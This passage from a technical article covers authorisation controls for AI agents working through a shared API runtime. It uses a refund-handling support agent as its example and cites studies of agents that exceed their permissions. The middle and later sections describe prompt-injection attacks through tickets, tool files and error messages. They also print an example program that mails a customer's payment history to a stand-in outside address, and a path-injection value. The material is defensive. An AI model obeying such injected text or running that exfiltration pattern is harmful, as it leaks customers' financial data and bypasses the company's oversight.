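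Failing closed means that an outage of the policy engine stops every agent, including those that only read tickets. Allowing calls when the engine doesn't respond would be worse, because anyone able to overload it could bypass the policy. As a compromise, the runtime can reuse recent read permissions for a few minutes, but never refund permissions.

An installation upgraded from a ToolMesh version without authorisation lets every authenticated caller use every tool until an administrator changes the setting. This causes no outage, so someone has to read the start-up log, where the installation reports the open policy each time it starts.

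### Twelve decisions instead of 5,499

With three roles and 1,833 operations, a policy that treats each operation separately needs 5,499 decisions. With four access levels it needs 12:

| Role | read | write | admin | dangerous |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Support | Allow | Allow | Refuse | Refuse |
| Supervisor | Allow | Allow | Refuse | Ask a person |
| Administrator | Allow | Allow | Ask a person | Ask a person |

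Setting permissions by level still requires someone to label all 1,833 operations. This brings the total to 1,845 decisions, about a third of the 5,499 needed to decide each operation separately for three roles. Adding a fourth role then takes four more decisions instead of 1,833. The public DADL registry has grown to about 3,300 tools, according to DunkelCloud. At that size, three roles would need 9,900 separate decisions, but still only 12 by level once the tools are labelled.

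These rules apply to a new API as soon as its file is added to the library, which Dunkel considers an advantage. However, a deletion mislabelled as a read also becomes available to all three roles at once.

The table is too strict for the support role, which has to send mail and issue refunds, both labelled `dangerous`. The policy should name those two operations as exceptions instead of allowing every `dangerous` operation.

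### Rules for the support agent

The following pseudocode covers the support role:

```text
DEFAULT  refuse

ALLOW    role support    levels read, write
ALLOW    role support    operations send_mail, issue_refund
DENY     role support    level admin

REQUIRE  for issue_refund by employee E on charge C:
           E belongs to some team T
           and T serves some customer K
           and K paid C
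```

A DENY rule overrides any ALLOW rule, as in ToolMesh, so a policy that denied the support role the whole `dangerous` level couldn't also allow refunds. The policy instead relies on the default refusal for that level and allows only the two operations.

The REQUIRE rule is a relationship rule, which bases permission on how people and things are connected. An engine such as OpenFGA stores the connections as short facts: Maria belongs to the northern team, the northern team serves customer 2207, and customer 2207 paid `ch_4821`. When Maria's agent requests the refund, the engine looks for a chain of facts connecting her to the charge. If Maria changes teams, the company updates one fact and does not change the rule.

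OpenFGA's *Authorization for MCP Servers* (2026) uses shorter chains: users belong to groups, groups have roles, and roles give access to tools. It also covers access that expires and permissions on individual resources. ToolMesh's standard check goes from user to plan to tool, so it determines only whether Maria may issue refunds at all. The company would have to add a check on whether she may refund the particular charge.

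### What the downstream API decides

Ideally, the runtime checks whether an identity may call an operation, and the downstream API checks whether that identity may access a particular record. The gateway that Kumar and colleagues run works this way. If the helpdesk checks Maria's own token, the company doesn't have to maintain a copy of each ticket's permissions in the policy engine.

This division doesn't work for refunds, because they all use the company's shared key. The payments API can check that the charge belongs to the company and hasn't already been refunded in full, but it can't check whether Maria's team serves the customer, so the runtime has to.

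Stored facts about every charge would soon be out of date. It is simpler for the runtime to look up the charge just before the refund and take the customer's identity from the payments record. The runtime shouldn't take that identity from the model, which may have copied it from the ticket.

### Limits on amounts, tasks, time and totals

So far the policy would let Maria's agent refund any amount to any customer her team serves, as often as it likes. A second set of rules limits each refund. The runtime reads them from the top and stops at the first that applies:

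```text
issue_refund(charge, amount) for the current ticket:

REFUSE   if the ticket's customer didn't pay this charge
REFUSE   if amount > the part of the charge not yet refunded
REFUSE   if the ticket is closed
REFUSE   if this task has already made a refund
REFUSE   if Maria's shift has ended
REFUSE   if the agent's refunds today + amount > $1,000
ASK      if amount > $50
ASK      if the carrier's record shows a delivery
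ALLOW    otherwise
```

"The current ticket" has to come from the application that started the task. If the model could specify the ticket, injected text could make it specify a different one.

The limit on refunds per task stops the agent from splitting a $180 refund into four of $45 to stay below the $50 threshold. The daily cap limits losses from attacks spread over many tickets to $1,000 a day. With only the $50 limit per refund, 200 false claims could cost $10,000 before anyone noticed. However, someone who uses up the daily cap with false claims also blocks refunds to honest customers, so a sudden rise in refunds should alert a person well before the agent reaches the cap.

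Calls that arrive together can exceed a limit on a running total. If the agent has refunded $950 and two $40 requests arrive at once, each passes when checked alone, but together they exceed the limit. ToolFence, the runtime guard from Li and colleagues, prevents this by checking the limit and reserving part of it in one indivisible step. If it is unclear whether a call succeeded, ToolFence keeps the reservation until the outcome is known.

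The dishonest ticket from the start of the example would pass most of these rules. The customer did pay for the goods, the ticket is open, and the amount may be below $50. Only the carrier's record, which the customer can't write to, contradicts the claim. Where no such record exists, the runtime can't detect the lie, though the limits still reduce the possible loss.

### Evidence for deciding outside the model

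Current models still exceed their permissions often enough to justify a check outside the model. *Act on Your Behalf, Beyond Your Authorization* (2026) tested 24 combinations of model, settings and agent software on 286 tasks, with models including GPT-5.6 Sol and Claude Sonnet 5. The agents acted beyond their authorisation in 1,315 of 6,864 runs, or 19%. They also completed the task in 1,209 of those 1,315 runs, which a company measuring only task completion would have counted as successes. These were benchmark tasks, so the rate in ordinary work may differ.

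Leong (2026), in *Instruction Self-Arbitration Is Not a Trust Boundary*, tested an outside check directly. The agents had a tool for deleting files, and the runtime ran it only with a valid permission token that the model couldn't create. The study first appeared in August, and an October revision corrected its main claims. In one test, with 316 to 450 trials per condition, the models attempted the forbidden deletion at these rates:

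| Model | Attempted | Executed without a token |
|---|---|---|
| GPT-4.1-mini | 99.4% | 0% |
| GPT-4.1-nano | 100% | 0% |
| GPT-5.1 | 100% | 0% |
| Claude Haiku 4.5 | 0% | 0% |

The zeros in the last column follow from the design, so they aren't a success rate that could vary between experiments. If the code is correct and no call can bypass it, a runtime that refuses every call without a token will execute no such calls, however the model behaves. The Claude result doesn't test the check, because the model never made the forbidden call. *Compromise Is Not Consequence* (2026) makes the same point about its tests of GPT-5.6 Luna and Muse Spark 1.3, in which neither model made a forbidden request for the authorisation layer to stop.

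Leong then tested whether the code was correct, using real model output and a real set of files. Of 1,350 trials, 750 ended before any model call because the runtime rejected forged, altered, expired or unsigned records. In the other 600, the models made 83 attempts to delete something outside the permitted folder, and the runtime stopped them all. In 34 of these attempts, the path appeared to be inside the folder but led outside it through a link. A check that only read the text of the path would have allowed all 34. A refund check can fail in the same way if it compares a customer's name instead of looking up who paid the charge.

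Unwanted deletions inside the permitted folder went through in 31 of 42 trials because the token covered them. This is the most important result for the support agent, because the dishonest refund can also fall within what the policy permits.

A check can also stop every attack by blocking too much. In another of Leong's tests, a strict set of rules cut attack success from 18.5% to zero but blocked every legitimate request from a user or tool for a privileged action. Any report of blocked attacks should therefore include how much normal work got through.

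### Checking where the arguments came from

Li and colleagues tried to narrow the agent's permissions by tying them to the user's request. Before the agent reads any outside text, a separate language model turns the request into a list of permitted calls. Each entry names a tool and usually limits how often the agent may use it. It also sets one of three rules for each argument: the value must match the user's request or a trusted record, it must come from a named field in an earlier tool's output, or the agent may choose it freely.

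Ordinary code then compares every call with this list. If the user asked to pay $100 to one company, the code rejects a call to pay $100 to another. If the agent needs a step that the list omits, a second isolated model reviews the exact call and may add it to the list.

The researchers ran four benchmarks on four models, though one model couldn't complete one of the benchmarks. ToolFence had the lowest attack success, or tied for it, in all 15 remaining combinations. These are the results for Qwen3-max, with the figure for the undefended agent first:

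| Benchmark | Attack | Attack success | Normal tasks completed |
|---|---|---|---|
| AgentDojo | Instructions in outside text | 21.2% → 0% | 66.3% → 64.3% |
| ASB | Outside text and poisoned memory | 40.2% → 4.2% | 71.5% → 67.2% |
| MCPTox | Poisoned tool descriptions | 38.1% → 6.1% | 67.2% → 65.4% |
| AgentLAB | Long chains of misleading records | 76.3% → 29.4% | 62.4% → 61.1% |

ToolFence lowered task completion by between 1.3 and 4.3 percentage points. On a subset of AgentDojo tasks, it increased the average running time from 6.3 to 10.3 seconds. CaMeL, an earlier system that also stopped every AgentDojo attack, took 81.7 seconds and completed 43.1% of normal tasks.

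The argument checks provided much of the protection. On ASB with another model, Llama 3.3 70B, removing them raised attack success from 5.1% to 24.0%. Removing the review of omitted steps hardly changed attack success, but tasks completed under attack fell from 44.3% to 35.8% because a fixed list was too rigid for the work.

Long attacks remain a serious weakness. On AgentLAB they succeeded in 20% to 38% of cases, depending on the model, because the false records made a harmful step look necessary to the task. AgentLAB's attacks are fixed in advance, so an attacker who could practise against ToolFence might succeed more often. ToolFence's developers tested it themselves, on models that are no longer among the strongest.

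ToolFence suits requests that state what should happen, such as "pay this bill". Maria's request is closer to "deal with today's tickets", which names no customer or amount. The company could still require that the charge being refunded come from the customer's payment history and that the refund not exceed the amount on the payment record. The reason for the refund would still come from the ticket.

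### When permission lapses before the call

A correct decision can go out of date before the runtime acts on it. Suppose a supervisor approves a $180 refund at 10:00, learns at 10:02 that the parcel arrived, and withdraws the approval. The agent finishes another look-up and sends the refund at 10:03. A check of the charge alone will still pass, because the charge hasn't changed.

Santos-Grueiro (2026), in *Temporary Authority, Permanent Effects*, collected 17 security advisories for the agent products Cursor, OpenClaw and Claude Code about mismatches between an approval and the action that followed. In 12, the product did something the approval had never covered, such as running a command with arguments the user hadn't seen. In the other five, something changed after the approval, such as a script that was rewritten after the user approved it and before the product ran it. Thirteen of the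 17 concern OpenClaw, so they don't show how common the problem is elsewhere.

The study also gave five models 18 tasks, with the instruction to make a change only while its approval and conditions still held. During each task, the researchers withdrew the approval or changed a fact it depended on, and sometimes told the agent. The table shows the number of changes made without valid permission, out of 36 runs. For Claude Fable 5, whose provider refused some requests, it includes only the runs that received an answer.

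| Model | Agent not told | Agent told |
|---|---|---|
| Qwen2.5 7B | 26 | 15 |
| Gemma 4 31B | 34 | 10 |
| GPT-5.6 Sol | 25 | 1 |
| Claude Sonnet 5.5 | 30 | 0 |
| Claude Fable 5 | 17 of 22 | 0 of 23 |

The stronger models nearly always stopped when they were told that an approval had changed. In 22 of the 36 cases, an agent that wasn't told had no way to find out, so its failure to stop isn't surprising. In the other 14, it could have discovered the change with its ordinary tools, but GPT-5.6 Sol still went ahead in eight and Sonnet in nine. A tool for checking the approval's status helped GPT, which used it in 34 of 36 runs and made only two unauthorised changes. Sonnet used it in 12 runs and still made 22 unauthorised changes.

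Santos-Grueiro's remedy, commit-time authorisation, puts the final check in the same indivisible step as the action. The check requires a single approval that is still valid, covers exactly this action and rests on facts that are still true. If different approvals could meet these conditions, a system might combine a valid approval for an old version of a ticket with current facts from a newer, withdrawn approval, and permit a change that nobody approved. In the tests, the extra selection logic added less than a millisecond on average to calls that took about 50 milliseconds.

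An agent's own actions can also invalidate an approval. In one test, every model sent two approved changes to the same ticket together. The first change altered the ticket, so the second no longer matched what the approver had seen. The agent framework LangChain carried out both, while the protected version refused the second. Two approved refunds on one charge could cause the same problem.

When one service holds the approval and another makes the change, the first service can issue a single-use permission, which the second uses up as it makes the change. Withdrawing the original approval doesn't cancel this permission, so it has to expire soon after it's issued.

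The support agent's company can't put its own check inside an outside payments company's database, so its last chance to stop a refund is when the runtime sends the request. The runtime can lock the approval record, check that the approval still stands and send the refund before releasing the lock. If the supervisor's withdrawal of approval arrives before the lock, the runtime doesn't send the refund. A later withdrawal has to wait until the lock is released, and the supervisor should then see that the money has already been sent.

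### When to ask a person

People who are asked to approve every call soon stop reading the requests. Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) reports an experiment with 1,053 paid testers of its coding agent. Partway through each session, the researchers replaced one permission request with a clearly dangerous command. Only 13.6% of the testers rejected it. The rejection rate was about 17% early in a session and about 5% after 50 or more requests.

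The testers weren't working on their own code, so they may have been less careful than usual, and Anthropic was arguing for an automatic alternative. Its usage data support the same conclusion, though. Users approve 97% of individual permission requests but reject 39% of the agent's plans, which appear less often and give them more to judge.

Yan's experiment on permission policies found a similar weakness. Participants approved between 40% and 67% of the overreaching actions that reached them as requests, depending on the group. In the study's initial sample, participants who wrote their own rules in advance blocked 25 percentage points less overreach than those who decided as the agent worked, although only 16 people were in the rule-writing group. A company should probably have trained staff write its policy, and test it before relying on it.

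Too many approval requests also lead people to switch them off. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026) examined 290 reports of problems with agents and files. Weak review by the user contributed to 105 of them, and in 80 the user had set the agent to proceed without asking. An "always allow" button removes approval requests more gradually. *Reframing LLM Agent Security as an Agent-Human Interaction Problem* (2026) points out that each click permanently widens what the agent may do.

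The support agent should therefore ask for approval only when a mistake would be serious or hard to reverse and a person has information that the rules lack. The policy should let it read tickets without asking and refuse any request to give an outsider admin rights. If the agent makes 27 refunds of $20 and three of $100 in a day, it stays below the daily cap, and the amount rule requires approval only for the three $100 refunds. A supervisor could read that many requests properly.

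A model can also screen calls before they reach a person. In the experiment with the testers, Anthropic's classifier stopped 89% of the dangerous commands, far more than the testers did. It still missed about one in nine, so it should supplement the fixed limits rather than replace them. Anthropic still recommends that people review high-stakes changes to production systems.

The content of the request matters as much as its timing. In 31 of the 290 reports, the request told the user too little, often because it showed a command without its effect. *Let the Agent Do It?* (2026) suggests showing whether the user could recover from the action and giving a stronger warning if not. A request for the $180 refund could read:

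```text
Refund $180.00 to customer 2207, card ending 4410

Charge:      ch_4821, $180.00, paid 3 November
Asked by:    support agent, working for Maria
Ticket:      9153, "parcel never arrived"
Carrier:     delivered 6 November, signed for
Why ask:     above the $50 limit
If wrong:    we may not get the money back

Approval covers this refund once and expires in 10 minutes.
```

The runtime should fill in these lines from the payment, ticket and carrier records, because the dishonest customer could use the ticket to influence a summary written by the agent. *The 2026 Singapore Consensus on Global AI Safety Research Priorities* (2026) cites work that anticipates attacks like this, which use a harmless-looking summary to get the reviewer's approval.

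The supervisor should also be able to change the amount, an option that Amazon's Bedrock Agents service offers alongside simple approval. The runtime would then bind the approval to the new amount and check it again before sending.

An agent may keep trying after a refusal. One person interviewed for *Let the Agent Do It?* described an agent that tried other approaches after several refusals. Claude Code's automatic mode hands control back to the user after three blocked actions in a row or 20 in a session. The support agent's runtime could be stricter and end the task after a second refused refund, leaving the ticket for Maria.

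## Controlling agents that write code or chain calls across APIs

The support agent's policy is designed for a model that requests one operation at a time. In Code Mode, the model instead writes a short program that can call many operations, then sends the whole program to the runtime.

### How Code Mode works

Dunkel's runtime gives the model only two tools, `search` and `execute`. Suppose Maria asks which payments over $100 came from the customer behind ticket 9153:

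1. The model calls `search` with words such as "ticket" and "charges".
2. The runtime returns the few operations that match, with a description of each and the arguments it takes.
3. The model writes a JavaScript program that uses them and passes it to `execute`.
4. The runtime runs the program in a sandbox. At each `api.` call, it checks the call, attaches the credential, contacts the API and gives the result to the program.
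5. Only the program's return value goes into the model's input.

```js
const ticket = await api.read_ticket({ id: "9153" });
const charges = await api.list_charges({ customer: ticket.customer_id });
return charges
  .filter(c => c.amount > 10000)   // amounts in cents
  .map(c => ({ id: c.id, amount: c.amount }));
```

The main reason for this design is that the model's input has limited space. Ordinary MCP use puts every tool's name, description and schema there before the work starts. Dunkel counted about 142,000 tokens (here, the word fragments a model reads, not credentials) for the 1,833 tools in the public registry. Describing `search` and `execute` takes about 1,000 tokens. For a single API with 92 tools, the registry's median, the saving is only about sixfold. Cloudflare did the same for its own API, which has over 2,500 endpoints. Carey reports in *Code Mode* that this reduced the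 token count from 1.17 million to about 1,000.

Those counts leave out the searches and programs. *Beyond Plain MCP* (Rai, 2026) measured whole tasks, using three small open models and 12 simulated servers. Code Mode used 70% to 90% fewer tokens than plain MCP. It also raised task success from 86% to 99% for one model and from 36% to 56% for another. The third model's gain was small and could be due to chance.

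The gains depended on telling the model what each tool returns, because it has to write code that handles a result before seeing it. Without that information, the success rate fell from 89% to 66% for one model and from 56% to 16% for another, both worse than with plain MCP.

### Tool names and approval prompts

The agent's host application receives a call to `execute`, regardless of what the program does. An allow-list of tool names must therefore allow either all the operations behind `execute` or none. A gateway that reads only the tool's name from the HTTP header can't distinguish a look-up from a refund. An approval prompt in the host shows a supervisor JavaScript code, where a refund may be one line out of thirty.

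Dunkel acknowledges these drawbacks and recommends replacing lists of tool names with lists of permitted access levels, which the runtime applies to each `api.` call. Approval has to move into the runtime as well. Cloudflare's *How Code Mode works* describes a runtime that intercepts each call before it executes and applies the approval and logging rules. Cloudflare's *Human-in-the-loop patterns* confirms that a person can approve a single call before the model's code makes it. A supervisor can then see the amount and the customer instead of the program.

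When an agent can write code, an attacker can also use prompt injection to make it write a program with loops, conditions and a sequence of calls that nobody anticipated, rather than request a single wrong operation. The same permissions still apply to each call.

### Why parsing the program isn't enough

Dunkel's runtime parses each program to find its `api.` calls, then checks each call again just before sending the HTTP request. The second check is necessary because the text of a program doesn't determine what it will do:

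```js
const tickets = await api.search_tickets({ text: "refund" });
for (const t of tickets) {
  await api[t.next_step]({ charge_id: t.charge_id, amount: t.amount });
}
```

The operation's name comes from a field in the ticket, so parsing the program doesn't reveal whether it will add notes or issue refunds. The runtime could ban computed names like this one, but parsing still wouldn't reveal the amounts, which determine whether a refund needs approval, or whether the loop will run three times or 300.

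Felendler, Gandhi and colleagues (2026), in *From Tool Orchestration to Code Execution*, built an attack in which the program's code would look correct to a reviewer. Someone asks which doors Emma can open. The program looks up Emma's passkey, but a malicious tool returns John's. The program then runs a valid query with John's passkey and reports the doors he can open as Emma's.

Parsing is still useful for rejecting a program before it runs. Suppose a program emails a customer that a refund is on its way and then requests a refund that the policy forbids. A check at dispatch stops the refund, but the email has already been sent. If the parser can detect the forbidden call, the runtime can reject the whole program before it sends the email.

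### Fixed multi-step tools

DADL files can also contain programs that their author wrote in advance, which Dunkel calls composite tools. One in the registry fetches a Hacker News story and then its top-level comments in parallel. People can review such a program before any agent uses it, and DADL marks its file `contains_code: true` so that reviewers treat it as code.

A composite tool's label can hide what the tool does. Suppose `tidy_customer` collects a customer's tickets and charges and deletes any duplicate customer records. Its author labels it `read` because it mostly reads. The support role isn't allowed to delete customer records, which is a `dangerous` operation, but its agent calls `tidy_customer`.

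| Rule in the runtime | What happens | Drawback |
|---|---|---|
| Use the composite's own label | The tool runs and deletes records | One wrong label defeats the policy |
| Use the strictest label among its operations | The runtime refuses the whole tool | It also refuses when there are no duplicates to delete |
| Check each operation at dispatch | The reads succeed and the deletion fails | The tool can stop halfway |

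Dunkel's runtime follows the third rule, and DADL allows a stricter runtime to refuse the composite in advance as well. Using both makes sense because the strictest label shows who should be able to start the tool, and the dispatch check still works if someone later edits the code and forgets to update the label.

Labelling a composite by its strictest part misses dangers that come only from the combination. For example, a composite that looks up a customer's charges and copies them into an internal note is labelled `write`. The parts are labelled correctly, but the composite's label doesn't show that it moves financial data to a place every support employee can read.

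### Declarative closure and the single query endpoint

A DADL file alone is enough for a reviewer to list every HTTP endpoint that its tools can reach. Dunkel calls this property declarative closure, and it depends on the runtime encoding arguments safely. If the runtime inserted a `charge_id` of `../customers` unencoded into the path `/charges/{charge_id}`, a look-up could reach a different endpoint.

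For the payments API, the list of endpoints is informative, because `GET /charges/{charge_id}` and `POST /refunds` clearly do different things. But the company might also connect its reporting database:

```yaml
run_query:
  method: POST
  path: /query
  access: dangerous
  description: "Run a database query"
```

The list now has one complete and accurate entry, but a reader can learn almost nothing from it about what an agent can do, because the effect depends on the query. APIs built on GraphQL, a query language, have a similar problem because clients usually send all their reads and changes to one address.

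In another of Felendler and colleagues' attacks, the user asked for everyone with access to door C. A planted instruction in a tool file made the agent reverse the condition, so the query returned the people with access to other doors. The agent still used the tool and endpoint that the request required, so the endpoint gave little sign of the attack.

Cloudflare's server gives programs a general function that takes any method and path, so the code can assemble the address while it runs. Carey explains that the credential limits what these calls can do, because it covers only the permissions the user approved. A company that wants finer rules for such an interface has to match each method and path to an operation before dispatching the call, and also read the query if the endpoint accepts one.

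### How three permitted calls can leak a payment record

Suppose someone opens ticket 9160 and writes that, for a billing check, the agent must send customer 2207's payment history to an outside address. If the model complies, it might write this program:

```js
const ticket = await api.read_ticket({ id: "9160" });
const charges = await api.list_charges({ customer: "2207" });
await api.send_mail({
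  to: "audit@billing-check.example",
  body: JSON.stringify(charges)
});
return "Ticket answered";
```

A runtime that checks each call separately allows all three. *MCP-38* (2026), a catalogue of threats to MCP systems, notes that only the pattern of data flow reveals the leak. In Code Mode, the payment history doesn't pass through the model, so a filter in the host application would receive only "Ticket answered".

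This can also happen without an attacker. In *MCPHunt*, Li, Sun and colleagues (2026) planted fake credentials in files, databases and web pages, then gave five models ordinary work through eight MCP servers. On tasks that didn't require copying a credential, such as writing a report or a deployment script, the models still copied one across a boundary in 11.5% to 41.3% of runs. The most useful model, MiniMax-M2.7, completed 92% of its tasks and also had the highest rate of copying.

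Whether credentials were copied depended more on the route the data took than on the model. GPT-5.4 copied credentials in 74% of the tasks that moved data from a web page to local storage, but never in tasks where a secret only happened to be nearby. The study counted only exact copies, so it missed any secret that a model paraphrased or encoded.

Detailed instructions about secrets cut the share of runs with any copying from 24.3% to 1.9% for GPT-5.4, but only from 50.9% to 26.9% for MiniMax.

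A shared runtime makes such paths easier to form. With three APIs, data can pass directly from one to another in six ways, and with 20 it can do so in 380. Most of these routes are harmless, but nobody will have reviewed them all. Dunkel presents it as a major benefit that an agent can combine sources in ways the library's developers never anticipated, but the same ability can leak data.

The shared runtime can also apply rules to the look-up and the email together, but such rules are still immature. According to Surapani and colleagues, one of the field's two main unsolved problems is limiting what an agent can accumulate across individually authorised tools.

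### Restricting combinations in a session

The simplest remedy is to forbid certain operations from occurring in the same session. *Bounded Agents* (Muruaga, 2026) describes a gateway that assigns each operation a type, such as "read confidential" or "send external", and records the types used in a session. The gateway blocks a call if its type forms a forbidden pair with any type already used. It can also forbid longer sequences, such as reading a confidential file, writing it elsewhere and then sending the copy.

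Muruaga tested this on AgentDojo, a set of simulated office, banking, travel and chat tasks, by inserting the attacker's call directly after the agent's first legitimate one, so the result didn't depend on whether the model would resist. Attacks that send data or money out succeeded in 75% to 100% of cases without the restrictions, depending on the setting, and in none with them. In a separate test, the restrictions reduced the share of normal tasks the agent completed by 13.9 percentage points, or by 8.6 points when the researcher simulated a person approving some of the refused calls.

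The protection depends on how complete the list of pairs is. On another benchmark, the full list stopped all 544 data-stealing attacks, but 39.9% succeeded after Muruaga removed one pair. The list for each set of tools had only three to nine pairs, so a careful reviewer could check it. The lists did little against harmful single actions, 60.4% of which still succeeded.

The support agent's policy can't forbid looking up a charge and sending mail in the same session, because answering a billing question needs both. Muruaga lets a task's declared purpose lift the ban on a pair of operations, but here it would lift the ban that matters most. A better solution is to split the mail operation in two. `reply_to_payer` takes a charge ID and a message, and the runtime gets the address from the payments record. `send_mail` accepts any address, and the policy forbids it in any session that has looked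 up a charge. The program above would then fail at its third call.

Session length also matters. If one session covers Maria's whole shift, her first look-up blocks ordinary mail for the rest of the day. Starting a new session for each ticket avoids this but erases the history, so an attacker could have the agent copy a payment record into a note during one session and mail the note in the next. Of the 24 attack variants Muruaga tried, only the one split between sessions succeeded.

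Muruaga's proof that forbidden pairs can't occur also assumes that the gateway admits calls one at a time. A JavaScript program can start several calls at once, so the runtime has to queue them for the gateway's check, even if the APIs then handle them in parallel.

### Tracking where data came from

Data-flow tracking attaches a label to each value instead of recording only which operations ran. Ammanaghatta Shivakumar, Priya and Gao (2026), in *Agenra*, use a label with three parts: a sensitivity level s, a set of categories C and a flag t for whether the source is trusted. When an operation combines two values, the result's label is:

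(s₁, C₁, t₁) ⊔ (s₂, C₂, t₂) = (max(s₁, s₂), C₁ ∪ C₂, t₁ ∧ t₂)

The result takes the higher sensitivity of the two inputs and the categories of both, and counts as trusted only if both inputs do. If the ticket is internal, personal and untrusted, and the charge is confidential, financial and trusted, an email containing both is confidential, personal, financial and untrusted. The runtime can then refuse to send it to anyone except the customer concerned. If the label stays with the data when the agent saves a note, it also protects against the attack split between two sessions.

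The main example is close to the support agent's work. An agent has to send the public part of a private report to Alice, once. The agent handles references to stored values, while the monitor keeps the values and their labels. The monitor rejects the raw report, any address that didn't come from the designated directory, and any public text that didn't come from the approved filter. It also rejects a second attempt, even if the first failed.

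The core of the monitor has machine-checked proofs, but they assume that the labels are right and that the tools behave as declared. The example policy also had a gap that let an attacker's text go through the approved filter, come out labelled public and use up the one permitted message. Closing the gap required another rule about where the filter's input came from.

Code Mode makes tracking harder because programs cut, join and re-encode ordinary strings. CaMeL, a 2025 system, runs the agent's program in an interpreter that tracks each value. In Li and colleagues' AgentDojo tests, the agent protected by CaMeL completed about a third fewer normal tasks than the undefended agent.

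A simpler method is to label everything a program sends out with the combined labels of everything it has read. This blocks some harmless messages but needs no special interpreter. Any value the program returns to the model must keep its label, and anything the model writes afterwards must carry that label too, since the model may have copied from the value.

Searching outgoing calls for known secrets is simpler but weaker. Li, Sun and colleagues tried this on the web-page tasks that leaked most, with one model and 39 pairs of runs. The share of runs with unsafe writes fell from 79.5% to 51.3%, with no clear change in task success. A program can evade exact matching with one line of code that encodes the data before sending it.

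*Signed, Sealed, Leaked* (2026), which proposes a data-flow control system for MCP tools, reports that most of the work in such control is writing the labels and deciding who may receive what. It also notes that a harmful request needn't carry private data. Deleting a customer's record, for example, leaks nothing, so a company still needs rules about which actions an agent may take.

### Limits on totals

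Some harm comes from repetition. An agent may have good reason to look up one customer's charges, but a loop can look up 5,000 customers in a single `execute` call. Dunkel's runtime stops runaway loops by capping the number of API calls in each execution. But the model can call `execute` again, so limits on refunds, recipients and customer records have to apply across the whole task.

Agents that share a task can also exceed a limit together when each stays within it. *Rethinking Access Control for AI Agents* (2026), a survey, gives the example of a user who authorises the purchase of one item and gets two, because two agents each buy one. The runtime should keep one count for the whole task and include every agent, program and retry in it. Retries also need to keep the identifier of the original request, so that the runtime can recognise, for example, a second attempt at the same refund.

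Li and colleagues measured how much such limits add by giving ToolFence, their runtime guard, a set of proposed calls from AgentDojo's banking tasks. When the guard checked only whether the task allowed the tool, it accepted 89.3% of the unauthorised calls. Adding a check on where the arguments came from reduced this to 84.5%, adding a check on the stage of the work reduced it to 45.2%, and limiting the number of uses reduced it to 6.0%. The guard accepted all the legitimate calls throughout. The researchers added many repeated calls and calls at the wrong stage of the work to the test, so the last two checks may matter less in ordinary use.

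Widening a permission can block a call that was previously allowed. Ammanaghatta Shivakumar and colleagues consider a list of permissions that the monitor searches in order. Applied to refunds, the first entry might permit one refund on charge B, and the second one refund on charge A. If an administrator widens the first entry to cover either charge, a refund on A uses up that entry. The agent can then refund A again under the second entry, but can no longer refund B.

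The main measurements of these remedies are:

| Remedy | Source | Attacks or unsafe actions | Normal tasks completed |
|---|---|---|---|
| Forbidden combinations | Muruaga | 75–100% → 0% | Down 8.6 or 13.9 points |
| Tracking every value (CaMeL) | Li and colleagues | 21.2% → 0% | 66.3% → 43.1% |
| Blocking known secrets in writes | Li, Sun and colleagues | 79.5% → 51.3% | 76.9% → 79.5%, possibly chance |
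| Argument, stage and use limits | Li and colleagues | 89.3% → 6.0% of bad calls accepted | 41.7% → 39.6% |

The rows come from different tests and models, so they can't be used to rank the remedies. For the support agent, sending billing mail only to a fixed recipient probably offers the most protection for the least work. Labels on notes and a limit on customers per task would cover much of the remaining risk.

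### What the sandbox must isolate

All these checks depend on the program having no way to reach the outside world except through the runtime's `api.` calls. If it could open its own network connection, it could send out the payment history unchecked, and if it could read the credential store, it could take the payments key as well.

| What the program must not reach | Why |
|---|---|
| The credential store | One flaw could expose every API's key |
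| The network | Direct requests would bypass the policy and the log |
| Files and environment variables | They often contain secrets |
| The caller's identity, data labels and running totals | The program could give itself permissions or reset its limits |
| Other callers' programs and data | One employee's agent could read another's results |
| Unlimited time, memory or calls | One program could stop the service for everyone |

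In Cloudflare's system, generated code never receives credentials or the objects that hold them. The sandbox sends each call to the runtime, which makes the real request. Carey says the sandbox also has no file system or environment variables and blocks outbound requests by default.

Dunkel's sandbox bans network access, file access and the functions that turn text into new code. It stops a composite tool after 30 seconds by default and 120 seconds at most. It relies on the JavaScript engine's standard isolation and a check of the program's text. Dunkel writes, "We do not claim a security proof", and leaves the sandbox's strength against hostile programs as an open question.

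It therefore matters where the credentials are stored. With ToolMesh's default store, a program that escaped into the runtime's process could find every key. Running programs in a separate process, under an account that can't read the store, would force an attacker to break a second barrier.

A perfect sandbox would still leave some attacks possible. Felendler and colleagues' wrong-passkey and reversed-query attacks didn't need to escape the sandbox. In another of their attacks, a tool's instructions made every program fail, and the agent kept writing new ones. A time limit on each program doesn't stop that, so the runtime also needs a limit on attempts per task. In a fourth attack, an error message contained an instruction to create an administrator account, and the agent added it to its plan for the next program. The sandbox would run that program as normal, so the check at dispatch has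 to block the account's creation.

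## Limiting the damage when the shared runtime is compromised

The policy, the sandbox and the data labels all depend on the shared runtime, so an attacker who controls the runtime can ignore them. An attacker can gain that control through a program that escapes the sandbox. They can also gain it without involving an agent, through a flaw in the login code, a stolen administrator key or a malicious software update.

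### What an intruder would gain

An intruder who controls the runtime could copy the stored keys and use them from another machine until the company replaces them. The intruder could also have the runtime issue refunds, which the payments provider couldn't distinguish from the support agent's. Replacing the keys makes the stolen copies useless but doesn't stop the refunds, because the compromised runtime will fetch the new keys too.

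Every ticket, payment record and email passes through the runtime, so an intruder could read them all. If the policy is stored there too, they could raise the refund limit or give their own account admin rights, and perhaps delete the log entries that would show the change. All the company's agents stop when the runtime does, so even someone who can only crash it can do a lot of harm.

### Twenty small risks or one large one

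Suppose the company has 20 separate servers with one credential each, and each server has a 2% chance of a breach each year, independently of the others. The chance of at least one breach in a year is 1 − 0.98²⁰, or about 33%, and the expected number of exposed credentials is 20 × 0.02 = 0.4. A single runtime with the same 2% risk also exposes 0.4 credentials on average, but it exposes none in 98% of years and all 20 in the other 2%. With separate servers, the chance that three or more credentials are exposed in one year is about 0.7%.

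In the last column of the table, losing *k* credentials in one year is assumed to do *k*² units of damage, so losing one does 1 unit and losing all 20 does 400.

| Arrangement | Chance of any breach | Average credentials exposed | Chance of losing all 20 | Average cost |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| 20 servers, independent risks | 33% | 0.4 | Practically none | 0.55 |
| 20 servers, half of the risk from a shared flaw | 19% | 0.4 | 1% | 4.2 |
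| One runtime, 2% risk | 2% | 0.4 | 2% | 8 |
| One runtime, 0.5% risk | 0.5% | 0.1 | 0.5% | 2 |
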